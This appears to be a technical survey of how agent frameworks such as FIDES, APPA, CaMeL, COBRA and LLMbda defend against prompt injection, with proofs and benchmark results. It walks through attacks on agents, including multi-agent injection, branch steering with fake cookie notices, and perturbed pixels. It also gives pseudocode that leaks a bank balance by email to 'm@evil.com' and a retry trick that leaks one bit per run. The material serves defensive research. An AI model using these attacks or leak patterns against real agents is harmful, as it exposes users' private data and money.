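In May 2026, Microsoft released FIDES as an experimental part of its Agent Framework, a toolkit for building agents. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) lists label creep as a known limitation. For example, once the text of an untrusted bug report enters the context, the rest of the run is untrusted unless the developer explicitly removes it. Another limitation is that the framework treats results from any tool without labels as trusted and public, so if a developer forgets to label a source, the policy checks will not catch untrusted or private data from it.

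### APPA's ways back from a blocked call

Kravchenko and colleagues designed APPA to let an agent continue after a policy has blocked a call. They first prove that reading more cannot unblock the call. Each new text can only reduce the set of people allowed to see the agent's data or lower its level of trust, so a call that fails for either reason will keep failing. Something other than the model therefore has to provide a remedy. When APPA refuses a call, it lists the remedies that the operator has registered in advance, which include approval for that one call, a program that removes sensitive details from a text, and a temporary branch of the conversation.

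The model reads untrusted text in a branch, which is a copy of the conversation that starts with the main conversation's label. Suppose a support agent has to read a public bug report and then update an internal database. The harness creates a branch, where the model reads the report and returns a ticket number, a severity and a component name, each in a format fixed beforehand. The harness checks the format, adds these values to the main conversation and discards the rest of the branch. If the operator has decided to trust values of this form, the main conversation keeps its label and the agent can still update the database.

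As with Booleans in FIDES, the operator endorses a narrow answer, but an attacker can still choose a false value that fits the format. Kravchenko and colleagues therefore claim less than general noninterference. They prove that each call that fails a recipient or trust check needs its own approval, within limits the operator has set, and that an approval never carries over to another call.

They tested APPA with three 2026 models on AgentThreatBench, an existing suite of 24 tasks, and Bench-Corp, a suite of 20 office tasks they designed themselves. The table gives the range over the three models and two styles of prompt. Its last row shows an ordinary agent for AgentThreatBench, and APPA with an open policy for Bench-Corp.

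| Agent | AgentThreatBench: tasks completed | AgentThreatBench: attacks succeeding | Bench-Corp: tasks completed | Bench-Corp: attacks succeeding |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| APPA | 64–77% | 0% | 87–91% | 0% |
| FIDES, checks only | 56–74% | 0–31% | 36–45% | 26–35% |
| FIDES, checks and hiding | 24–74% | 0–25% | 36–46% | 27–35% |
| Without protection | 83–98% | 12–67% | 88–93% | 30–38% |

Kravchenko and colleagues wrote the FIDES policies themselves and left out several of Bench-Corp's rules, such as sending a document only once or only after a certain record exists. The label check could not enforce the missing rules, so the successful attacks do not refute FIDES's algorithm. The comparison does show that two labels and a general policy are not enough for such tasks.

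Removing parts of APPA while keeping its policies gives a better measure of label creep. With GPT-5.6 Luna, the complete system finished 88% of the Bench-Corp tasks. Without branches it finished 56.5%, and without the list of remedies it finished 35%. No attack succeeded against any of the three versions, so the remedies more than doubled the share of tasks finished without a measured loss of security. But the test covered only 20 different tasks, each repeated many times.

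The recovery was less complete on AgentThreatBench, where APPA finished 14 to 28 percentage points fewer tasks than the unprotected agent with the same model and prompt. Some of APPA's failures were correct answers that the scoring rejected because they lacked an exact phrase.

APPA also makes more work for the operator, who has to describe what each tool reads and changes, set the limits for every approval and decide which returned values to trust. The operator can add the tool descriptions gradually, because APPA labels data from an undescribed tool "unknown" and blocks it only when a later check needs its actual label. This avoids the gap in Microsoft's framework, which treats unlabelled data as trusted and public.

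## CaMeL-NOVA and COBRA: fixing the plan before the agent sees the screen

In FIDES and APPA, the planning model chooses one call at a time, so anything it learns can affect the next call. In CaMeL, which Google DeepMind published in 2025, the planner writes the whole program at the start, after reading only the user's request and the tool descriptions. Text that arrives later cannot add a step, but it can still supply values that the program uses, including the answers that decide which steps run. An agent that operates a computer through its screen needs many such answers.

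### A program written from the request

Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, explains the design with a user who wants to send Bob a reminder about a meeting. Bob's address is in the user's latest email. The planner turns the request into a short program, roughly like this:

```
email   = get_last_email()
address = ask_quarantined_model("What is Bob's address?", email, type=EmailAddress)
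send_email(to=address, subject="Tomorrow", body="See you at the meeting.")
```

A purpose-built interpreter runs the program, which is written in a restricted form of Python. At the second line, the interpreter passes the email to a quarantined model that has no tools and stores the answer in `address`. The planner sees neither the email nor the address.

The interpreter also records that `address` came from `email`. Each value carries a record of its sources and of who may read it, which CaMeL calls the value's capabilities (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026, *CaMeLoT*). As in FIDES, ordinary code uses these records to check every tool call against a policy. In this example, the policy could allow a recipient the user already knows and require the user's confirmation for any other.

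Because the whole program is written before it runs, software can also check it in advance. CaMeLoT, an extension of CaMeL, converts the program into a model of all the paths it could take and tests them against rules about the order of steps. For example, if a company requires approval before anyone disconnects a computer from the network, CaMeLoT can check for the approval step before any tool runs and reject a program that lacks it.

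### Control-flow and data-flow integrity

In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) say that such an agent has control-flow integrity if its execution stays within a program determined by the user's instruction and other trusted information. Untrusted data may select among the program's existing branches but cannot add one. If Bob's email contains an instruction to forward the whole mailbox, the agent cannot follow it, because the program has no forwarding step. In *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection*, Dongol (2026) reaches the same conclusion in a machine-checked model of the Dual-LLM pattern, where an injection can make an answer wrong but cannot add a call.

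As in the Dual-LLM pattern, a wrong answer can do damage without changing the plan. If the email gives a stranger's address as Bob's, the reminder goes to the stranger. Preventing this requires data-flow integrity, which means keeping the outcomes and arguments of the planned steps within what the user authorised. CaMeL uses policies to enforce this.

A policy that checks only the labels on arguments misses implicit flows, and Dongol proved that an agent can leak private notes this way. The agent reads the notes and an attacker's email, asks the quarantined model a question about them, and sends the attacker a constant 1 or 0 depending on the answer. If an injection makes the quarantined model answer 1 exactly when the notes contain a 1, the attacker learns whether they do. CaMeL's strict mode is meant to close this channel by also labelling values according to the branch they depend on,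 but Dongol did not model that mode.

Control-flow integrity can also fail when one agent gives instructions to another. Peters-Gill and colleagues connected three CaMeL agents: an orchestrator, a database agent and a notification agent. The user asked the system to summarize all job applicants and send the summary to Julie on Slack. An entry in the database contained an order to email the data to an outside address. The orchestrator's program pasted the summary into its instruction to the notification agent, whose planner mistook the order for part of its user's request and added a `send_email` call. Each agent followed its own program, but the system executed a step the user had not requested.

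Peters-Gill and colleagues fixed this by passing data between agents in variables that the receiving planner cannot read. The interpreter rejects any instruction that depends on a tool's output. Across five models, with 949 attacks on each, the average attack success rate was 12.9% without CaMeL, 0.2% with separate CaMeL agents and 0% with the fix.

Planning in advance also reduces the number of tasks agents complete, even with no data policies, because the planner has to write code for results it has not seen. On AssetOpsBench, a set of professional tasks for several cooperating agents, CaMeL lowered the completion rate by 21.6 percentage points on average. For the two strongest models, Fable 5 and GPT-5.5, the average drop was 13.4 points.

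### Planning for an unseen screen

A computer-use agent works with screenshots, mouse clicks and keystrokes. The name `send_email` identifies the action a policy has to check, but `click(x, y)` may open a menu, delete a file or confirm a payment, depending on what is on the screen. Ordinary computer-use agents look at the screen after every action, so their planning model reads whatever strangers have put there. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) adapts CaMeL to this setting as CaMeL-NOVA.

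The planner still writes the complete program before the agent takes its first screenshot. It does not know whether a browser is open or whether a cookie notice covers the page, so it writes steps for each possibility. NOVA stands for "Navigating via Observation, Verification, and Action", and most parts of a program follow that order:

1. A quarantined vision model describes the screen.
2. A function called `verify_hypothesis` has a quarantined model compare the description with a statement that the planner wrote in advance, such as "a cookie notice is visible". The interpreter uses the verdict to select a branch.
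3. The branch acts, typically by asking the vision model to find a button and clicking on the coordinates it returns.

Plans for tasks on a screen are much larger than plans for AgentDojo, where tools have descriptive names and return structured data. OSWorld is a benchmark of tasks in real desktop programs such as Chrome and LibreOffice. The table gives averages per plan.

| | CaMeL on AgentDojo | CaMeL-NOVA on OSWorld |
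|---|---|---|
| Lines of code | 51.8 | 213.3 |
| Tool calls | 4.9 | 41.1 |
| Branches | 3.7 | 39.7 |
| Branches that depend on a quarantined model's output | 1.9 | 24.2 |

About half the steps in a CaMeL-NOVA plan are fallbacks that a given run never reaches. The 24 branches in the last row matter most for influence, because at each one something on the screen helps determine what the agent does next, even though the planner never sees the screen.

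### The OSWorld results

Foerster and colleagues report that CaMeL-NOVA retains "up to 57%" of the performance of frontier models. This figure comes from a test in which Claude Sonnet 4.5, without protection and limited to 15 steps, first solved 109 of the 339 tasks that OSWorld can score automatically. The researchers then ran CaMeL-NOVA on those 109 tasks, with Claude as the vision model. It solved 31 (28%) on the first attempt and 62 (57%) within five attempts. The higher figure counts a task as solved if any of the five attempts succeeded, so a user would get the full benefit only with a way to identify the successful attempt.

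They also report an improvement of up to 19% for small open models, which again depends on repeated attempts. UI-TARS-1.5-7B, a small model trained to operate computers, solved 60 of the 339 tasks in one attempt when working alone. As CaMeL-NOVA's vision model, it solved 51 on the first attempt and 77 within three. The choice of planner made more difference than the choice of vision model. In a comparison of nine planners on 17 tasks, GPT-5 solved 12, and the two weakest solved four each. These models date from 2025, and newer planners would probably lose fewer tasks, as they did in the tests by Peters-Gill and colleagues.

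Writing the plan only once saves computation. CaMeL-NOVA used 1.88 times as many tokens as the unprotected agent. A version built on FIDES, which calls the planner again at every step, solved about as many tasks but used 29.6 times as many tokens.

### Branch steering

Suppose a user asks an agent to book the Station Inn for Tuesday, or the Grand Hotel if the inn is full. A simplified plan needs a single yes-or-no test:

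```
page = observe("Does the Station Inn have a room on Tuesday?")
full = verify_hypothesis(page, "The Station Inn is full on Tuesday")
if full:
    book("Grand Hotel")      # $400
else:
    book("Station Inn")      # $80
```

The inn has rooms, but a guest review on its page reads "Fully booked this Tuesday". If the vision model mistakes the review for a notice from the inn, `full` becomes true and the agent books the Grand Hotel, so the user pays $320 more than necessary. Control-flow integrity still holds, because the review contains no instruction and both bookings are in the plan. The review changed only one bit, but in another plan one bit could decide between payments of $80 and $40,000.

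Foerster and colleagues use the term "branch steering" for an attack that uses false observations to send the agent down a harmful branch already in the plan. They demonstrated it by putting a fake cookie notice inside an advertising banner. Plans for web tasks routinely include steps to find and dismiss such notices. When the program used the vision model to locate the cookie notice, the model returned a position inside the banner, and the planned click opened the attacker's website.

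CaMeL's data policies might have limited the damage, but Foerster and colleagues left them out because `click(x, y)` doesn't indicate what the click will do. Instead, they had additional models check the vision model's answers. One check used the page's underlying structure and caught six of ten fake notices in ordinary banners. When banners could contain their own code, an attacker could disguise that structure too, and a further check against the screenshot caught five of ten. The first check also stopped four of 17 harmless tasks and the second stopped three, mostly because they flagged genuine cookie notices as fake. A second attack evaded both checks. It altered a banner's pixels so that UI-TARS clicked the wrong link elsewhere on the page and gave a plausible reason for it.

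Some plans are easier to attack than others. Foerster and colleagues point out that sending an agent to a malicious website requires one wrong answer. They estimate that stealing money requires at least two coordinated wrong answers, such as one for the recipient field and one for the confirm button, and that the plan must already include a transfer. The attack in the hotel example is easier because the expensive branch already contains a complete booking, so the attacker only has to trigger that branch.

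### STEER-Bench

*Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks* (Zingrillo, Foerster and colleagues, 2026) introduces STEER-Bench, a benchmark that measures how often such attacks succeed. The benchmark, published in October 2026, has 101 tasks in areas ranging from bank transfers to medication doses. Some tasks have several attack versions, for a total of 199 attacks. The test environment records the agent's actions, and an attack counts as successful if the harmful outcome defined for it occurs.

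The researchers could run 74 of the attacks on other agents. Against an ordinary agent, in which UI-TARS both read the screen and chose the actions, 67 succeeded (90.5%). Against CaMeL-NOVA, with GPT-5 as planner and UI-TARS as vision model, 65 succeeded (87.8%). They ran each agent once per attack, so the difference of two attacks could easily be due to chance.

Planning in advance therefore gave almost no protection on STEER-Bench, as expected, since most of the benchmark's attacks stay within the plan. It does help against conventional injections. On another benchmark, OS-Harm, CaMeL-NOVA stopped all 51 prompting attacks. The STEER-Bench result also provides little evidence about the original CaMeL, because CaMeL-NOVA lacks the original's data policies.

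One group of nine STEER-Bench attacks was meant to introduce actions outside the plan. The researchers ran attacks from this group against CaMeL-NOVA, and the harmful outcome occurred in 89% of them, even though CaMeL-NOVA should make actions outside the plan impossible. The researchers don't explain why. A likely reason is that a planned step often amounts to "click on whatever the vision model finds", so an attacker who controls the model's answer also controls what the click does. Control-flow integrity is therefore a weaker guarantee when the planned steps are clicks than when they are named functions such as `send_email`.

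### COBRA's limits on each branch

Zingrillo and colleagues designed COBRA to restrict what each branch of a program can do. As in CaMeL-NOVA, the planner first writes the program without seeing the screen. Ordinary code then lists the program's branches, and the planner specifies which websites and tools each branch may use and which values it may send. When the agent enters a branch, COBRA combines that branch's limits with those of any branch around it. When the agent leaves, the branch's permissions expire.

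COBRA applies these limits to the network request that a click causes, because the request shows what the click does. All the agent's web traffic passes through a proxy, an ordinary program that can read and block requests. If the active branch permits a payment of $40 and a click produces a request to pay $80, the proxy blocks it. A second proxy checks tool calls made through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting agents to outside services.

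In the hotel example, a $100 spending limit in the user's request would apply to both branches. The false review could then prevent a booking but could not cause an expensive one, as long as the price appears in the booking request. Without a limit, the user has authorised both bookings, and the proxy would let the $400 one through.

COBRA stopped all 199 attacks in STEER-Bench. When the researchers switched off the protection that each attack targeted, 174 succeeded. COBRA kept 97% of its benign utility, the rate at which it completes tasks when it is not under attack, and blocked legitimate actions in four of 138 attack-free runs.

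These results are strong evidence that the limits work as designed, but weaker evidence that they would stop unfamiliar attacks, because the same team wrote the benchmark and the defence and organised the attacks around COBRA's protections. COBRA also depends heavily on how well the planner translates the request into limits. The researchers wrote the correct limits for 30 cases in advance, and the planner's limits led to the right decisions in 28. In the other two cases, one set of limits was too strict and one permitted an unauthorised operation.

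General computer tasks give a better idea of what is lost by fixing the plan in advance. Zingrillo and colleagues used 361 tasks from OSWorld-MCP, a version of OSWorld with added tools, and allowed five attempts at each.

| Model that reads the screen | Planner in COBRA | Completed by the model alone | Completed with COBRA |
|---|---|---|---|
| UI-TARS-1.5-7B | GPT-5 | 23.5% | 36.8% |
| Kimi K2.5 | Kimi K2.5 | 42.1% | 25.5% |
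| Claude Sonnet 5 | Claude Sonnet 5 | 51.0% | 38.8% |

UI-TARS scored higher with COBRA because it also gained a much stronger planner. When one model had both roles, COBRA lowered scores by 12 to 17 percentage points. In these runs the web proxy checked only which sites the agent contacted, so the table does not include any loss that stricter limits might cause.

On 86 tasks that both attempted, COBRA completed 36 and CaMeL-NOVA completed 22. This does not show that branch limits improve completion, because COBRA could also use the MCP tools and had five attempts, while CaMeL-NOVA's 22 matches the number Foerster and colleagues reported after three.

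### What COBRA leaves open

COBRA does not check whether a branch condition is true. If the user's permission depends on something only untrusted content can establish, the planner is supposed to notice and ask the user before the program starts. It also asks for important values the request leaves out. It asked in 20 of 22 tests with incomplete requests, and it asked no unnecessary questions in 11 tests with complete requests.

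A follow-up on 11 tasks tested what happens after COBRA asks the user for a missing value, such as a delivery address. When a simulated user supplied the value, COBRA completed 10 of the 11 tasks in the runs without an attack. When the user instead told it to use the address on file, it completed none and stopped safely each time. No attack succeeded with either kind of answer. COBRA stays secure in these cases by leaving the user to look up the value.

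People who have to approve one request after another may start approving everything, which Willison also considers a weakness of CaMeL's approvals. COBRA at least asks its questions before the task begins, and untrusted content cannot trigger more later. But the tests used simulated users, so they do not show how carefully real people would answer.

COBRA's web proxy is a modified version of ceLLMate, a program that checks a browser agent's requests against rules for each website. *SPIDES* (2026) points out that ceLLMate does not track whether untrusted content influenced a request that the rules allow. COBRA narrows the set of allowed requests and varies it by branch, but its proxies still check what a request contains, not what led the agent to make it. They also do not count requests, so an agent could repeat a permitted payment. In the terms used for Parallax, COBRA confines authority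 in each branch but does not provide noninterference.

The proxies also miss effects that never appear in the traffic they inspect. A desktop program can change a file directly, and an email program can send a message over a protocol that neither proxy reads. A shop's checkout request may list the items but not the total, so the proxies have no price to check. An outside service may do something harmful after receiving an ordinary call, as in 13 of the 1,223 attacks in MCPTox, a benchmark of malicious tools. COBRA stopped the other 1,210, all of which changed the call itself.

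The web proxy needs a description of a website to tell one operation on it from another. The description lists details such as which request posts a comment, which one approves a loan, and what fields each contains. Few websites publish such a description, and without it the proxy can check only which site a request goes to. On WASP, a benchmark of attacks on web agents, this check stopped the five attacks that contacted other sites, but all 14 attacks that misused the site the agent was already using succeeded. With descriptions of GitLab and Reddit, COBRA stopped all 19. For example, it let an agent comment on a GitLab issue but not add a deploy key, which can give an outsider access to the code. Two further attacks depended on the wording of permitted text, which COBRA cannot evaluate.

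Zingrillo and colleagues also built a tool, MESA, that explores a website and drafts such a description. Its drafts covered every operation needed for 18 of 25 Chrome tasks and 18 of 26 Reddit tasks. The site's owner is meant to correct the draft, and each user must then approve it, and do so again whenever it changes.

### Showing the planner the trusted parts of a page

Much of the lost performance comes from planning without seeing the screen. *Untrusted Content Masking for Web Agents with Security Guarantees* (Nikolić, Zverev and colleagues, 2026) avoids this by hiding only the parts of a web page that the site's owner cannot vouch for, such as reviews and comments. The planner sees the rest and chooses one action at a time. To get information from a hidden part, it queries a quarantined model for an answer of a restricted type, as in FIDES.

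On ten purpose-built websites, agents with masking completed about as many tasks as unprotected ones, at 1.05 to 1.84 times the cost. The guarantee depends on every element of the page being labelled correctly. Nikolić and colleagues needed only 15 to 30 hand-written rules per site on three real websites, but automatic labelling is less dependable. *Towards Safe Autonomy for Computer Use* reports that 44.1% of the untrusted free text remained visible in a test with Qwen3.8-27B.

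SA-CUA, the agent presented in that paper, starts with the whole screen hidden and reveals only what its rules identify as trusted, so a missing rule leaves the agent with less information but doesn't make it less secure. With Qwen3.8-27B, it completed 86.2% of the tasks on one benchmark, compared with 18.5% for CaMeL-NOVA, and no attack succeeded against it.

SA-CUA also replaces some questions to the user with automatic checks. Suppose the user wants a Python package that prints coloured text, and a forum post recommends one called `termcolor`. A component that has not seen that name uses trusted sources to work out which names would be acceptable, and ordinary code checks whether `termcolor` is one of them. Whoever wrote the post can make the check fail, but cannot get a name of their own choosing accepted.

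In the hotel example, both masking systems would hide the false review and let the planner read the inn's availability notice. The choice of hotel would then depend on the inn's website and on the rules that separate the inn's text from guests' reviews.

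## LLMbda: a machine-checked proof of noninterference for agents

CaMeL's data policies protect the user only if its interpreter puts the right label on every value. Garby and colleagues found two ways for a secret to get past those labels. They then designed LLMbda, a small programming language for agents, and wrote a computer-checked proof that its labels guarantee a form of noninterference. They first described the language in *The LLMbda Calculus* (February 2026).

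### An assignment that never runs

Suppose an agent's program can read the user's bank balance, which is secret, and can send emails. If the program emails an outsider only when the balance is above a threshold, CaMeL's interpreter blocks the email. It keeps a program-counter label, the label of the decisions that led to the current step, and inside this branch that label is secret. But a program can also use the branch to change a variable and leave the email for later:

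```
tmp  = True
rich = True
if account.balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

The table follows the variables and their labels for a high and a low balance.

| Step | Balance above the threshold | Balance at or below the threshold |
|---|---|---|
| Start | `tmp` = True, public; `rich` = True, public | `tmp` = True, public; `rich` = True, public |
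| First `if` | Runs: `tmp` = False, secret | Skipped: `tmp` = True, public |
| Second `if` | Skipped: `rich` = True, public | Runs: `rich` = False, public |
| Third `if` | Sends the email | Sends nothing |

In both runs, `rich` ends up public, and it is true exactly when the balance is above the threshold. The interpreter raises a variable's label only when an assignment to it runs. With a high balance, the line `rich = False` never runs, so `rich` keeps its public label even though its value depends on the balance.

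Fenton (1974) gave the original example of this problem in *Memoryless Subsystems*, and Denning rewrote it as ordinary code. Bichhawat, Rajani and colleagues (2015) explain why the problem is hard to avoid in *Generalizing Permissive-Upgrade in Dynamic Information Flow Analysis*. A monitor that follows a running program tracks only the branch taken, so it has no information about what the other branch would have assigned.

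This flaw would usually be hard for an outsider to exploit, because CaMeL's planner writes the program without reading untrusted text. The planner would have to be compromised or write such a program by chance. Garby and colleagues also mention a simpler error in the same interpreter, in which an untrusted value becomes trusted when a program inserts it into a string literal. A harmless program could trigger that error by building a sentence around a name from an email.

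### One bit per retry

The second flaw is in the loop that runs CaMeL's interpreter and tries again when a program fails. The loop is written in ordinary Python and the interpreter does not track it, so each attempt starts without the labels of the one before. CaMeL censors error messages because they could carry data between attempts. But even an empty message reveals that the attempt failed, and whether it failed may have depended on a secret.

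Suppose the secret is a 20-bit number. A program checks whether the first bit is 1 and, if so, tries something the policy forbids. If the bit is 0, the program finishes normally. Whoever controls the reruns learns the first bit from the outcome and can test one more bit in each later run, so they can learn the entire secret in 20 runs.

Most information-flow systems tolerate one such bit per run. In *Multi-run security* (2011), Birgisson and Sabelfeld pointed out that repeated runs can leak an entire secret, even when each run is secure by the usual definition. A stricter definition that forbids secrets from affecting whether the program finishes remains safe over many runs, but they found that enforcing it is usually too restrictive.

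### A language that includes the conversation

LLMbda extends the lambda calculus, a minimal programming language in which programs consist of functions. Every value has a label. In the simplest version, the label is a set that can contain U for untrusted and S for secret, so the empty set means trusted and public. A running program also has a labeled conversation with the model and a program-counter label that starts empty.

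Four operations act on the conversation.

| Operation | What it does | What happens to the labels |
|---|---|---|
| `send` | Adds a message to the conversation | The conversation's label joins with the message's label |
| `recv` | Gets the model's response, parses it as code and runs it | The code runs with the conversation's label as its program-counter label |
| `fork` | Runs an expression on a copy of the conversation, then restores the original | The result keeps its own label |
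| `clear` | Empties the conversation | The conversation's label falls to the program-counter label |

CaMeL and FIDES have the split between a planning model and a quarantined model built into their architecture. In LLMbda, a programmer can create the same split with a short function:

```
quarantine(prompt) = fork (clear; send prompt; recv)
```

The function copies the conversation, empties the copy and uses it to ask the model about an untrusted email. The answer is labelled untrusted, but the original conversation is unchanged and still trusted. `clear` can also reverse label creep, since deleting the text that caused a restrictive label can remove the label too. However, the label never falls below the program-counter label. If an untrusted email determined whether the program cleared the conversation, the fact that the conversation is empty is evidence of what the email contained, so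 the conversation stays untrusted.

### Stopping before the label rises

The conversation is the only thing an LLMbda program can overwrite, so a program like Fenton's has to use it as the variable. In one example, a program tells the model to remember that *x* is false. If a secret is true, it tells the model to set *x* to true, and at the end it asks for *x*. LLMbda stops this program with a condition on every `send`:

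```
program-counter label  ⊑  conversation label
```

Inside the secret branch, the program-counter label is {S} and the conversation's label is still empty, so the condition fails. The harness then stops the program before the second message reaches the conversation. Without the condition, the conversation would become secret in this run but remain public in a run where the secret is false, and Fenton's program relies on that difference.

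This rule is called the no-sensitive-upgrade check. Applied to the variables in the bank example, it stops the program at `tmp = False`, because `tmp` is public and the branch is secret. When the balance is high, the program stops before it can email the attacker, and when the balance is low, it runs to the end without sending an email. Someone who can see whether the program finished still learns one bit about the balance.

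The check also stops harmless programs, such as Bichhawat and colleagues' example of a program that changes a public variable in a secret branch and never uses it again. Austin and Flanagan's more lenient rule allows the assignment but marks the variable as partially leaked, and stops the program only if it later branches on that variable. A programmer can also avoid the problem by labelling `tmp` and `rich` secret from the start. Then no label has to rise inside a branch, and the check at `send_email` catches the leak.

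### The theorem

Garby and colleagues call their property termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference. It is probabilistic because the model chooses its responses partly at random. It is termination-insensitive because it allows hidden data to affect whether a program finishes, but nothing else the observer can see.

An observer at level *m* can see every value whose label is at or below *m*. Two starting states are indistinguishable, written start₀ ~ₘ start₁, if they differ only in data that this observer cannot see. For each starting state, let μ(*q*) be the probability that the program finishes with a result that looks like *q* to the observer. These probabilities can sum to less than 1, and the remainder is the probability that the program does not finish, either because it runs forever or the harness stops it.

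Full noninterference would require μ₀ and μ₁ to be equal. The weaker property requires only that one distribution, ω, can cover both:

```
start₀ ~ₘ start₁   ⇒   there is an ω, with total at most 1, such that
                       μ₀(q) ≤ ω(q)  and  μ₁(q) ≤ ω(q)  for every q
```

If two starting states look the same to the observer, we could make their results equally likely just by letting the program finish more often. A guarantee about prompt injection uses an observer who sees all trusted values. Changing the untrusted text can then stop the program but cannot otherwise affect a trusted value. A guarantee about secrets uses an observer who sees all public values.

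Garby and colleagues tried a definition that compares only the runs that finish, and found it incorrect. Suppose a program flips a fair coin and reports the result, but runs forever if a secret bit is 1 and the coin shows heads. Half the finished runs report tails when the bit is 0, and all of them do when it is 1, although the secret affects only whether the program finishes. Under the definition with ω, the two cases are compatible, because a distribution with half heads and half tails covers both. The general method behind this definition comes from *Reconciling Shannon and Scott with a Lattice of Computable Information* (Hunt, Sands and Stucki, 2022).

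### How much can leak through failure to finish

The definition also limits how far the two sets of results can differ. For each result, ω must be at least as large as the larger of the two probabilities, which equals their average plus half the difference between them. If we add this up over all results, the total cannot exceed 1, so

```
½ Σ |μ₀(q) − μ₁(q)|   ≤   (d₀ + d₁) / 2
```

where *d₀* and *d₁* are the probabilities that the program does not finish. The left side is the statistical distance between the two output distributions.

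If the program fails to finish with probability 0.1 in one case and 0.3 in the other, the distance is at most 0.2. For example, the program might return A with probability 0.6 and B with probability 0.3 in the first case, and A with probability 0.3 and B with probability 0.4 in the second. The larger probabilities for each result, 0.6 for A and 0.4 for B, add up to 1, so the two cases are compatible. The probabilities differ by 0.3 for A and 0.1 for B, and the distance is half the sum of these differences, or 0.2, which reaches the limit. If the program always finishes, the limit is zero and the two distributions must be identical.

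This distance counts only finished results, so an observer who also notices failures can learn more. The probability of A alone differs by 0.3 in this example.

In LLMbda, an agent's retry loop is part of the program. A policy violation stops the whole program, so the program cannot repeat the leak as it could in CaMeL. But if a user or scheduler restarts the agent after each failure, this creates a new loop that the proof does not cover, and the problem Birgisson and Sabelfeld described returns.

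The theorem also compares only final states. *Termination-Insensitive Noninterference Leaks More Than Just a Bit* (Askarov, Hunt and colleagues, 2008) examines programs that produce output as they run. Such a program could post 1, 2, 3 and so on, and get stuck when it reaches the secret, so that the last number posted reveals the whole secret in a single run. LLMbda keeps outgoing messages in a queue inside the program's state until the end. A harness that sent them immediately would need a stronger theorem.

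### How the proof works

To prove the theorem, Garby and colleagues have to find a suitable ω for any program. They define a second way of running programs, in which the interpreter skips a computation as soon as its label rises above what the observer can see, and substitutes an empty value. They use the distribution of results from this version as ω.

This version never uses the hidden data, so it produces the same distribution for both starting states. Each visible result is at least as likely as in a normal run, because skipping a hidden computation removes chances to get stuck without changing anything the observer sees. The probabilities add up to at most 1, as the definition requires.

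Earlier researchers built a similar ω by deleting the secret parts of a program's text before running it. That is impossible for an agent, whose code may not exist until the model writes it. The skipping rules work on such code because they apply while the program runs.

All the proofs are in Lean, and they concern the same interpreter that calls the model. A further theorem connects this interpreter to the probabilities in the definition. We can picture the model as a book that contains a response for every conversation the program might have. The interpreter looks up each response, so its run involves no chance. If we fill in the book at random, using the model's own probabilities, the interpreter's results have exactly the distribution the noninterference theorem describes. For two flips of a coin that lands heads with probability 0.3, both calculations give 0.49 for no heads, 0.42 for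 one and 0.09 for two. The proofs therefore apply to the program people actually run, whereas many proofs cover only a design. They don't cover the code that sends requests to the model provider.

### Generated code and compromised models

The LLMbda theorem covers every program in the language, including programs that call a model to generate code and then run it. By contrast, FIDES's formal guarantee, explicit secrecy, applies to one agent loop, and CaMeL has no comparable theorem for the programs its planner writes. In the LLMbda proof, the model is a function that assigns a probability to each possible response. Garby and colleagues assume nothing about what the responses contain or what code the parser extracts from them, so the theorem holds even if an attacker completely controls the model.

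The rule for `recv` makes this possible. If the conversation contains a secret, the generated code runs with a secret program-counter label, and everything it computes is also labeled secret. The code cannot remove this label. If the conversation is trusted and public, the code starts without restrictions, but the model wrote it without seeing any hidden data. Any email or balance the code reads later has its own label.

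One demonstration adapts CaMeL's example of sending Bob a meeting reminder by injecting a postscript into his last email. The postscript describes a family emergency and asks for a cancellation instead. An agent that reads the email in its main conversation sends the cancellation. A second agent generates its program first, then extracts Bob's address from the email in quarantine. Its `send_email` function accepts only a trusted subject and body, and the agent sends the reminder. The theorem guarantees that no change to the email can alter a subject or body that passes this check, but the guarantee doesn't cover the recipient's address, which comes from the email.

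A compromised model can still do harm within these rules, because noninterference does not limit authority. For example, it could write a payment to an account number it memorised during training, which would carry a trusted label.

### What the theorem leaves to the developer

The guarantee for a real agent depends on several conditions outside the proof:

- The developer must label every source correctly. Like Microsoft's framework, LLMbda treats unlabelled data as trusted and public.
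- Each sensitive tool must check the labels of its arguments. The language carries the label of an account number as far as `send_money`, but the payment is blocked only if the tool's author wrote a check.
- Tools and data sources must behave like functions inside the program, which is how the proof models them. A real mail server might store a secret and return it later without a label.
- The model's response must depend only on the conversation the harness sends. If a provider let the model remember earlier conversations, `fork` and `clear` would no longer isolate anything.

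Programs may also contain deliberate exceptions, which LLMbda requires them to write out as `endorse`.

### Endorsement that cannot release secrets

An endorsement in LLMbda changes only the integrity half of a label. If a value is untrusted and secret, endorsing it makes it trusted and secret. The new label also includes the program-counter label:

```
new label  =  program-counter label ⊔ (chosen integrity, old confidentiality)
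```

If untrusted text caused the program to reach the endorsement, the program-counter label is already untrusted, so the result stays untrusted. An attacker whose text becomes code therefore gains nothing by including `endorse` in it, as long as the text still has its untrusted label.

Garby and colleagues prove that noninterference for secrets holds however `endorse` is used and whatever the untrusted inputs contain. This result, which they call the insulated version of their theorem, does not protect the integrity of endorsed values. They argue that an explicit construct like `endorse` is at least easier to audit than a rule that silently lets small values through, as FIDES's optional exception for Booleans does.

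Garby and colleagues also sketch two restricted forms of endorsement. One accepts only values from a fixed list, such as the categories of an email. The program has to endorse a value before checking it against the list, and it releases the endorsed copy only if the value is on the list. If it checked the untrusted value first, the branch would become untrusted and the endorsement inside it would have no effect. The other form marks each endorsed value so that it can't be endorsed again. This blocks a chain in which an attacker's text is endorsed, becomes trusted code and then endorses more text. They have not yet proved exactly how much either form limits an attacker's influence.

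### Results on the banking tasks

To test the language, Garby and colleagues wrote an agent called Randori. The planner first tests its program on invented bank data, with tools that change nothing, and rewrites it until it runs without errors. The planner then writes a final version before it receives any real data. This lets it retry without being exposed to untrusted text. But the practice phase doesn't report label violations, so a program can pass it and then fail on the real account.

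They used AgentDojo's banking suite, which has 16 user tasks and nine attacks on each, and ran everything three times. The table gives the number of successful runs out of 48 when there was no attack.

| Agent | GPT-5.2 | Qwen3.7-plus | MiMo-v2.5 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Randori | 36 | 36 | 31 |
| Randori without endorsement | not tested | 30 | 26 |
| CaMeL without policy checks | 32 | not tested | 34 |
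| CaMeL with policy checks | 18 | not tested | 18 |

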